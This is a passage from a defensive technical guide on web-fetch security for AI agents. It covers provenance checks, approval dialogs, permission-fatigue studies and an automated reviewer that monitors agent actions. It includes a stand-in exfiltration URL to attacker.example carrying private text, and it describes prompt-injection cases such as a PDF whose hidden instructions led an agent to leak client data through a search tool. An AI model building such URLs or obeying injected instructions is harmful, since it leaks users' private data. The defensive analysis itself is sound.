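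| `http://install-notes.md/`, a squatted page already in the index | Fetch | Fetch if the user or a tool result supplied it | The agent reads hostile content |
| `https://northbank-business.example/login`, a phantom domain registered yesterday | Hold until the crawler finds it | Refuse if only the model has written it | The agent reaches a fake login page |
| `http://HEARTBEAT.md`, typed by the user as a filename and auto-linked before the agent saw it | Fetch if the software treats it as the user's address | Fetch | The agent reads a stranger's instructions |
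| `https://attacker.example/collect?data=bicycle`, built by the model from private text | Hold | Refuse | The attacker receives the private text |

A crawler records that a page is public, whoever owns it, so a domain squatter can get a hostile page into the index by publishing it and waiting. Anthropic's rule stops the fetch if the model wrote the address from memory, but not if a search returned it. If either system allows the fetch, the agent may read an injected instruction, but the provenance check can still block a second request that would carry private data out.

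OpenAI's rule probably stops the fetch from the phantom domain because the crawler has had little time to find the page. That protection ends once the page is in the index, but it is still useful because a reputation check is weakest for new domains. Anthropic's rule doesn't depend on the domain's age. The tool refuses the address while it appears only in the model's output, but accepts it if the user copies it from Claude's answer into a new message. It also accepts a wrong domain from a vendor's installation guide if the guide reached Claude through a permitted source.

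The provenance check receives misleading information when chat software turns a filename into a link. The user typed `HEARTBEAT.md`, and the chat software added `http://` before passing the message on. Anthropic's tool accepts the complete address because it appears in a user message, although the user never meant to supply one. ChatGPT may do the same. As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT treats an address in a user's message as safe for the rest of the session. If ChatGPT doesn't count this address as the user's, the fetch depends on whether the crawler has indexed the site.

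An older version of ChatGPT's check was especially permissive towards misread filenames. Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot* found that it accepted any domain with no subdomain, path or query, such as `http://README.md`. This exception made some sense as a defence against leaks, because an attacker can create unlimited subdomains to represent different secrets but would have to pay for each separate domain. However, it did nothing to prevent a request to the wrong host.

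A filename might also reach the agent as plain `HEARTBEAT.md`, and the model might then add a scheme such as `https://` itself. Anthropic's documentation doesn't specify whether the tool treats the address with and without the scheme as the same. A builder can check by repeating the earlier test with a filename that is also a .md domain they own.

Both rules handle addresses containing private data well because the companies designed them for this case. An address that the model has just invented shouldn't be in the index or in any permitted source. However, an attacker could publish addresses for many likely words in advance, including "bicycle", which would again let the model reveal data by choosing among them. With Anthropic's default settings, a client tool could also make the address acceptable by repeating the model's text.

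Both rules therefore protect secrets better than they prevent requests to the wrong destination. The third case shows this most clearly, because a request to `http://HEARTBEAT.md` reveals almost no private information, but the returned page can contain instructions that the agent mistakes for its own task list. An agent with a provenance check still needs to check the host, keep filenames as text and treat the returned page as untrusted.

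### Building a provenance check

Few builders can run their own web crawler. Asking an outside search service whether it knows an address is a risky substitute, because the question itself sends the full address, including any secret in it, to that service. Anthropic's approach is easier to copy, since it needs only a record of the conversation:

1. Save each user message and tool result before any linking software changes it.
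2. Extract the complete addresses and record the source of each one, such as the user, a search result, a fetched page or an email.
3. When the model requests a fetch, look for the exact address in this record. Ignore the model's own output and any tool result that merely repeats it.
4. Apply a rule to each source. For example, the software could accept addresses from users and search results but hold those from emails and fetched pages.
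5. Check the host and every redirect, as in the previous section, before sending a request.

The first step fixes the `HEARTBEAT.md` case, because the original message contains no scheme and so no complete address to record. It works only where the builder controls the software that creates the link. Links already in an incoming email or forum page need the label comparison described earlier.

Either rule will stop some useful fetches. A public-index rule holds back company intranet pages, personal download links and very recent news. A conversation-based rule prevents the model from opening a documentation page whose address it remembers correctly, or from changing the page number in an address to see the next set of results. Under either rule, the agent can often find another source by searching. As with an allowlist, a trial in logging mode shows which fetches the check would stop.

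The check also has to cover every tool that can contact a host. Willison describes an attack on Notion 3.0 that Abi Raghuram reported in September 2025. A PDF contained hidden instructions for the agent to put a company's client data into an address and pass that address to the search tool. The search tool accepted addresses as well as search terms, so a check on the fetch tool alone would have missed the leak.

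Rehberger found a similar gap at OpenAI, whose early protection was missing from ChatGPT's apps for macOS and the iPhone. He thinks such gaps could keep appearing, because developers of a new feature may not know that the check exists. A builder can find them by repeating the previous section's test with every tool, including search and image display, using an address that the agent has to put together itself.

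## Asking a person before a fetch

When a provenance check holds back an address, the software can refuse the fetch or ask the user to approve it. Fetch approval requires a person's consent before the agent requests an address.

Asking the user works well for misread filenames because someone who typed `HEARTBEAT.md` knows whether they meant a file or a website. Neither a list of TLDs nor an index of public pages contains that information. Wang, Li and Tian (2026) argue more generally in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem* that some instructions to agents are ambiguous because the user left something out, and that a better model can't supply what is missing. Of the 21 production agents they examined, 15 ask for approval while working.

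The software also has to ask for approval early, because nobody can take back what a server has already received, whereas an owner can restore a deleted file from a backup. The DNS lookup reveals the host, so the software should ask before the lookup, not just before the web request.

### People approve by habit

Users approve 97 per cent of Claude Code's permission requests, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026). An earlier account, Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, gives 93 per cent. These rates alone don't prove carelessness, because most requests are probably for harmless commands that even a careful reader would approve. Users reject 39 per cent of the plans Claude presents, which suggests they look at plans more closely, although a plan also gives them more to disagree with.

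Better evidence comes from an experiment in which Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers for a coding study without telling them what it was measuring. Partway through each session, one permission request showed a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6 per cent) rejected it. The rejection rate was about 17 per cent when the command appeared early in a session and about 5 per cent when it appeared after 50 or more requests.

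The testers were not working on their own code, so they had less to lose than a developer at work. Anthropic also had a stake in the result, since it was about to make automated review the default. Neither point easily explains why people became less careful as the number of requests grew.

In *Let the Agent Do It?*, Salerno, Gao and colleagues (2026) interviewed 18 software practitioners and surveyed another 115. Of the 107 who answered the survey's questions about permissions, 47.7 per cent said they read requests carefully, 33.6 per cent said they skim them and 20.6 per cent said they approve them by default (respondents could choose several answers). A third said they had become less careful over time, and the true share may be higher because people were describing their own habits.

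Nearly all respondents (98.1 per cent) were more willing to grant read-only access than other permissions. A fetch looks like reading, but it also sends the address to someone else's server, so a user who assumes it is read-only may approve a fetch that leaks information.

Frequent approval requests also lead people to turn them off. Anthropic reports that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in a mode that bypasses permission checks. By June 2026, 49.5 per cent of active command-line users had written a rule allowing some shell commands to run without approval, often covering a whole programming language such as Python. A Python script can contact any host, so a rule like this can also let an agent fetch links without approval unless network access is restricted separately.

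*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of agents damaging files and finds that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those 105, the user had let the agent act without asking. In 31, the request showed a command but not its effect. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine but doesn't show what the script will do, which could include contacting a website.

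Older research on browsers and phones found similar habits. Wang and colleagues cite a click-through rate above 90 per cent for warnings about website certificates. But *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* (2026) cites a 2013 study by Akhawe and Felt as evidence that a warning's effect depends strongly on its design, so one browser's click-through rate may not apply to a new fetch dialog.

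### People misread addresses

Even an attentive user may not understand the address. Two studies from 2020, before today's agents existed, tested this directly.

Reynolds, Kumar and colleagues (2020), in *Measuring Identity Confusion with Uniform Resource Locators*, asked 94 people which website each of about 20 addresses led to. Participants identified 93 per cent of the real addresses but only 40 per cent of the deceptive ones, such as `https://fb.com@n593.biz`, whose host is `n593.biz`. Only 16 per cent consistently looked for the full domain name, yet 96 per cent believed their own methods protected them well enough.

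Albakry, Vaniea and Wolters (2020), in *What is this URL's Destination?*, showed 23 addresses to 1,929 people. About a third always chose the organisation named in the address, wherever the name appeared. Only 8.3 per cent could reliably tell a name in the domain, as in `profile.facebook.com`, from one in the subdomain, as in `facebook.profile.com`. Most of these people would probably also misread `modelcontextprotocol.io.example.com`, which would have passed Claude Code's faulty comparison.

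Browser makers had tried to help by displaying a site's identity more clearly. In *The Web's Identity Crisis*, Thompson, Shelton and colleagues ran a large field experiment on one such display, which shows the verified identity behind a website's certificate. Reynolds and colleagues report that the display didn't help people judge identity, and that changing how the address was highlighted didn't significantly help them detect phishing either.

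A more recent experiment shows that a different kind of request can work better. In *URL Inspection Tasks* (Lain, Nakatsuka and colleagues, 2025), participants played an employee working through a mailbox of real and phishing emails. The table gives the results for the 1,573 participants in the United States, out of 2,673 in three countries.

| What happened after a click | Phishing links visited | Genuine links visited | Median time |
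|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 74.5% | 90.6% | none |
| A page showed the address and asked for confirmation | 57.2% | 87.9% | 3 seconds |
| The person dragged the parts of the address into place | 61.0% | 89.4% | 6–7 seconds |
| The person had to pick, highlight or type the domain | 35.0% | 82.1% | up to 10 seconds |

Dragging the parts into place took longer than a plain confirmation but didn't protect people better, so the extra effort alone doesn't explain the improvement in the last row. Picking, highlighting or typing the domain makes people commit to a destination, and the software can then warn them if the address leads elsewhere. People who typed the domain visited 17 per cent of the links with a misspelt domain, while people who got no help visited 79 per cent.

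This method works if the user has a destination in mind, such as their bank. It doesn't help much when an agent is researching an unfamiliar subject and has chosen the site itself, because the user doesn't know which domain to expect. But users don't need to know anything about web addresses to say whether `HEARTBEAT.md` is a file.

### Nobody may be there to answer

Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* objects that users who must approve each action can't start a large task and walk away. An agent working overnight would stop at its first unanswered request and wait until morning.

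If a request for approval expires, the software should refuse the fetch and let the agent continue any work that doesn't depend on it. Fetching anyway would avoid a delay, but an absent user would then in effect approve every fetch.

### Asking every time, or following the user's rules

*Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026) compared three designs with 113 people who don't work in software. Each person supervised a simulated assistant through 18 actions. Seven of these went beyond the user's instructions, such as buying a $25 airport lounge pass or reading private messages.

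| Design | Requests per person | Total time | Unrequested actions blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| The person approves every action | 18.0 | 142 seconds | 59.6% |
| A model allows some actions and asks about the rest | 10.0 | 120 seconds | 53.9% |
| The person sets a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each type of action | 10.9 | 129 seconds | 39.6% |

The rules protected people least. Participants set 114 of the 140 rules to "ask", which left the decision for later. When they were then asked about 199 unrequested actions, they approved 133. Yan recruited some of this group after random assignment had ended, so the comparison is not fully randomized. Even people who were asked to approve every action let through four in ten of the unrequested ones.

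Yan notes that Claude Code already has allow, ask and deny rules that can cover domains. Setting every domain to "ask" would leave the user with the same decisions as before. A builder can help users more by supplying firm defaults, such as denying sites that let anyone collect incoming requests, than by giving them an empty list of rules to fill in.

### Asking once per domain

Claude Code's sandbox asks the user about each new domain. *Beyond permission prompts* (Anthropic, 2025) reports that sandboxing reduced permission requests by 84 per cent in the company's internal use. That figure also covers requests for commands and files, so it doesn't show how much asking once per domain reduces permission requests for fetches.

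Approving a domain approves every path and query on it. If a user allows `notes.example` so that the agent can read an article, the agent could later send the same host a query containing private text without asking again. Anthropic warns that any approach that permits outgoing network traffic can leak data the agent can read.

Wang and colleagues criticise "always allow" buttons because they keep widening an agent's access and nothing narrows it. A builder can limit this by making each approval expire when the session ends and by asking the user again if an address on an approved domain contains a query they haven't seen.

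### OpenAI's dialog for unverified addresses

When an address isn't in its public index, OpenAI's software can show the user a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". The dialog displays the address with a warning that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with another site. The user can then copy the link or open it. OpenAI recommends that users who notice something odd leave the link alone and ask the model for another source or a summary.

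Most pages an agent tries to fetch are probably already public, so the dialog should appear less often than one shown before every fetch. That may help people notice it. In the survey by Salerno and colleagues, 63.6 per cent said they check unexpected requests more carefully.

The dialog's wording suits data leaks better than misread filenames. If the dialog appeared for `http://HEARTBEAT.md`, the user would read a warning about conversation data, see none in the address, and might reasonably open the link. Neither button lets them explain that they meant a file. Copying the link isn't safe either if the user then pastes it into a browser, because the server would receive the same query.

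### Letting an automated reviewer decide

Claude Code's auto mode replaces most approval requests with a classifier, a model that judges actions before they run. On 14 August 2026 Anthropic began making it the default for new sessions on its Pro, Max, Ultra and Team plans, except for users who had already chosen another mode. In October Anthropic announced the same default for most Claude apps on the Pro, Max and Team plans.

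The classifier checks web fetches unless a user's narrower rule already allows them, but it doesn't check file reads or edits to files inside the project. It receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. Anthropic withholds the pages the agent has read so that a hostile page can't influence the classifier directly. Anthropic also withholds the agent's explanations so that the agent can't argue for a bad decision.

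The classifier therefore can't tell whether the agent found an identifier in a tool's output or made it up. The same should be true of web addresses, and a provenance check can supply the missing information. For a misread filename, the classifier may already have the information it needs. If the user wrote "check HEARTBEAT.md" and the agent tries to fetch `http://HEARTBEAT.md`, both strings are in the classifier's input. Neither of Anthropic's accounts includes a test of this case.

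Anthropic tested the classifier on three sets of actions:

- It wrongly blocked 0.4 per cent of 10,000 real tool calls by Anthropic's employees.
- It missed 5.7 per cent of 1,000 synthetic attempts to leak data, some of which put credentials in web addresses.
- It missed 17 per cent of 52 real actions in which Claude had gone beyond the user's instructions.

The last figure is based on only 52 cases, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from 9 to 30 per cent. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the danger but wrongly treated something in the session as the user's consent.

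The classifier also judged the dangerous commands from the experiment with 1,053 testers. Anthropic reports that it blocked 937 of the commands, or 89 per cent. Of the 116 it missed, the testers rejected only six. Also asking a person about everything the classifier allowed would therefore have added little protection in that test, and would have produced many more requests.

The results for prompt injection are harder to credit to the reviewer. Trajectory Labs, which Anthropic commissioned, made 720 attack attempts against three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. But attacks on Anthropic's latest models succeeded only 0.09 per cent of the time even without permission checks, so the models themselves resisted almost all of them. The comparison is clearer for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, where attacks succeeded 19.03 per cent of the time with full access and 5.83 per cent with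 the automated reviewer.

When Claude Code's classifier blocks an action, Claude receives the reason and can try something else. After three blocks in a row or 20 in a session, the software asks a person, or ends the process if the agent is running without a user interface. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to production systems. InfoQ's *Anthropic Details How It Contains Claude Across Web, Code, and Cowork* (2026) reports that the company also argues for fixed limits on files, networks and execution instead of relying only on permission requests or the model's own safeguards.

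### The cost of 200 fetches a day

This example compares three policies for an agent that makes 200 fetches in one session. It assumes the fetches go to 40 domains, all new to the user, and that ten of the addresses are missing from a public index. One fetch is hostile and is equally likely to come at any point.

People took a median of 3 seconds to respond to a plain confirmation in the study by Lain and colleagues. Yan's participants took about 8 seconds per request when they approved every action. The example assumes that a user has a 17 per cent chance of rejecting the hostile fetch during the first 50 requests and a 5 per cent chance after that, based on Anthropic's rates for dangerous commands.

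| Policy | Requests | Time at 3 seconds each | Time at 8 seconds each | Chance that the user stops the hostile fetch, if asked about it |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ask about every fetch | 200 | 10 minutes | 26 minutes 40 seconds | 8% |
| Ask once per domain | 40 | 2 minutes | 5 minutes 20 seconds | 17% |
| Ask only about unverified addresses | 10 | 30 seconds | 1 minute 20 seconds | 17% |

The 8 per cent is an average over the day: (50 × 17% + 150 × 5%) / 200. Under these assumptions, asking about ten addresses protects the user better than asking about all 200 if the hostile address is among the ten at least 47 per cent of the time. The threshold is 47 per cent because 47 per cent of 17 per cent is 8 per cent. That condition may fail if attackers wait until their pages are in the index.

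The times don't include the disruption to someone's work, which may matter more than the seconds spent on the dialog. An automated reviewer that wrongly blocked 0.4 per cent of fetches would block about one harmless fetch a day. The agent would usually try another route without involving the user.

All three chances are low, and they are based on shell commands rather than addresses. A builder should replace them with figures from the product's own users, gathered by occasionally showing them a harmless test request that a careful person ought to reject.

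### What a useful request shows

For the misread filename, a request could contain the following:

- **Host:** `heartbeat.md`, a website under Moldova's TLD
- **Source:** your message, "check HEARTBEAT.md before lunch"
- **Data in the address:** none besides the name
- **Choices:** "This is a file", "Open the website" or "Don't open it"

The dialog has to show the host without any action from the user. In *Eyes on the Phish(er)* (2024), participants rarely hovered over links to check the address. The two who did so on phishing emails reported them. Most saw the address only in the browser, after clicking. The dialog should show the host separately from the rest of the address, in large fixed-width letters. In the experiment by Lain and colleagues, merely displaying the address this way and asking for confirmation reduced visits to misspelt domains from 79 to 58 per cent.

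*When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* points out that the information needed to judge an action may not be in the action itself. `http://heartbeat.md` looks the same whether the user typed a filename or a search engine returned a website, so the approval dialog should show the text the link came from. The software should copy that text from its own records rather than have the model explain the link, because an injected instruction could make the model describe a hostile address as something the user had asked for. If the text came from a web page or an email, the dialog should name that source, since an attacker may have written it.

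The software should show the person the data a fetch would send in readable form, for example as "word: bicycle". OpenAI says its software can show users what a request would transmit. If the address contains a long encoded string that the software can't decode, a person can't judge it either, so the software should refuse the fetch.

The answer "This is a file" tells the agent why the person refused the fetch and what to do next. A plain "no" might lead it to try `https://heartbeat.md` instead. Salerno and colleagues similarly recommend that permission systems distinguish between rejecting one action and rejecting a whole approach. The software can remember the person's answer and treat the same name as a file for the rest of the project.

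An approval should apply only to the address on the screen, so it doesn't cover a redirect to another host.

If the agent asks for approval through a messaging service, the service can fetch the address to generate a link preview before the user answers. The agent's software should therefore put the address in code formatting and turn off previews for approval messages.

### When not to ask

*A Two-Dimensional Framework for AI Agent Design Patterns* (2026) describes an order for such decisions. The software first applies rules that deny an action, then rules that allow it, and sends only what remains to a person. It classifies actions by how much damage they could do and whether anyone could reverse them. For fetches, a builder could extend this order as follows:

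1. **Refuse** if the address contains a password or another secret, or if a rule blocks the host. Asking would give a tired user the chance to approve a leak. Anthropic designed Claude Code's auto mode never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside destination, although the classifier missed some such attempts in testing. A user who wants to send them has to leave that mode or run the command personally.
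2. **Read the local file** if the name matches one in the project and the address is only that name with `http://` or `https://` in front. This step has to come before the provenance check, which might accept the address because it appears in the user's message. If the user did mean the website, they can correct the agent, and no data has left in the meantime.
3. **Fetch** if the host is on the allowlist or the address passes the provenance check, and the usual checks on redirects succeed.
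4. **Try another source** if the task doesn't depend on this particular page. An agent that wants an unknown blog post about a programming error can often find the same answer in the official documentation.
5. **Ask** if the agent still needs the address and someone is there to answer. Otherwise, skip the fetch and list the address in the final reply as plain text, so that the user can decide later.

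The user should be able to answer the remaining requests from their own knowledge. They might recognise a page on the company's intranet or a download link a colleague sent, or know that a filename refers to a document on another computer.
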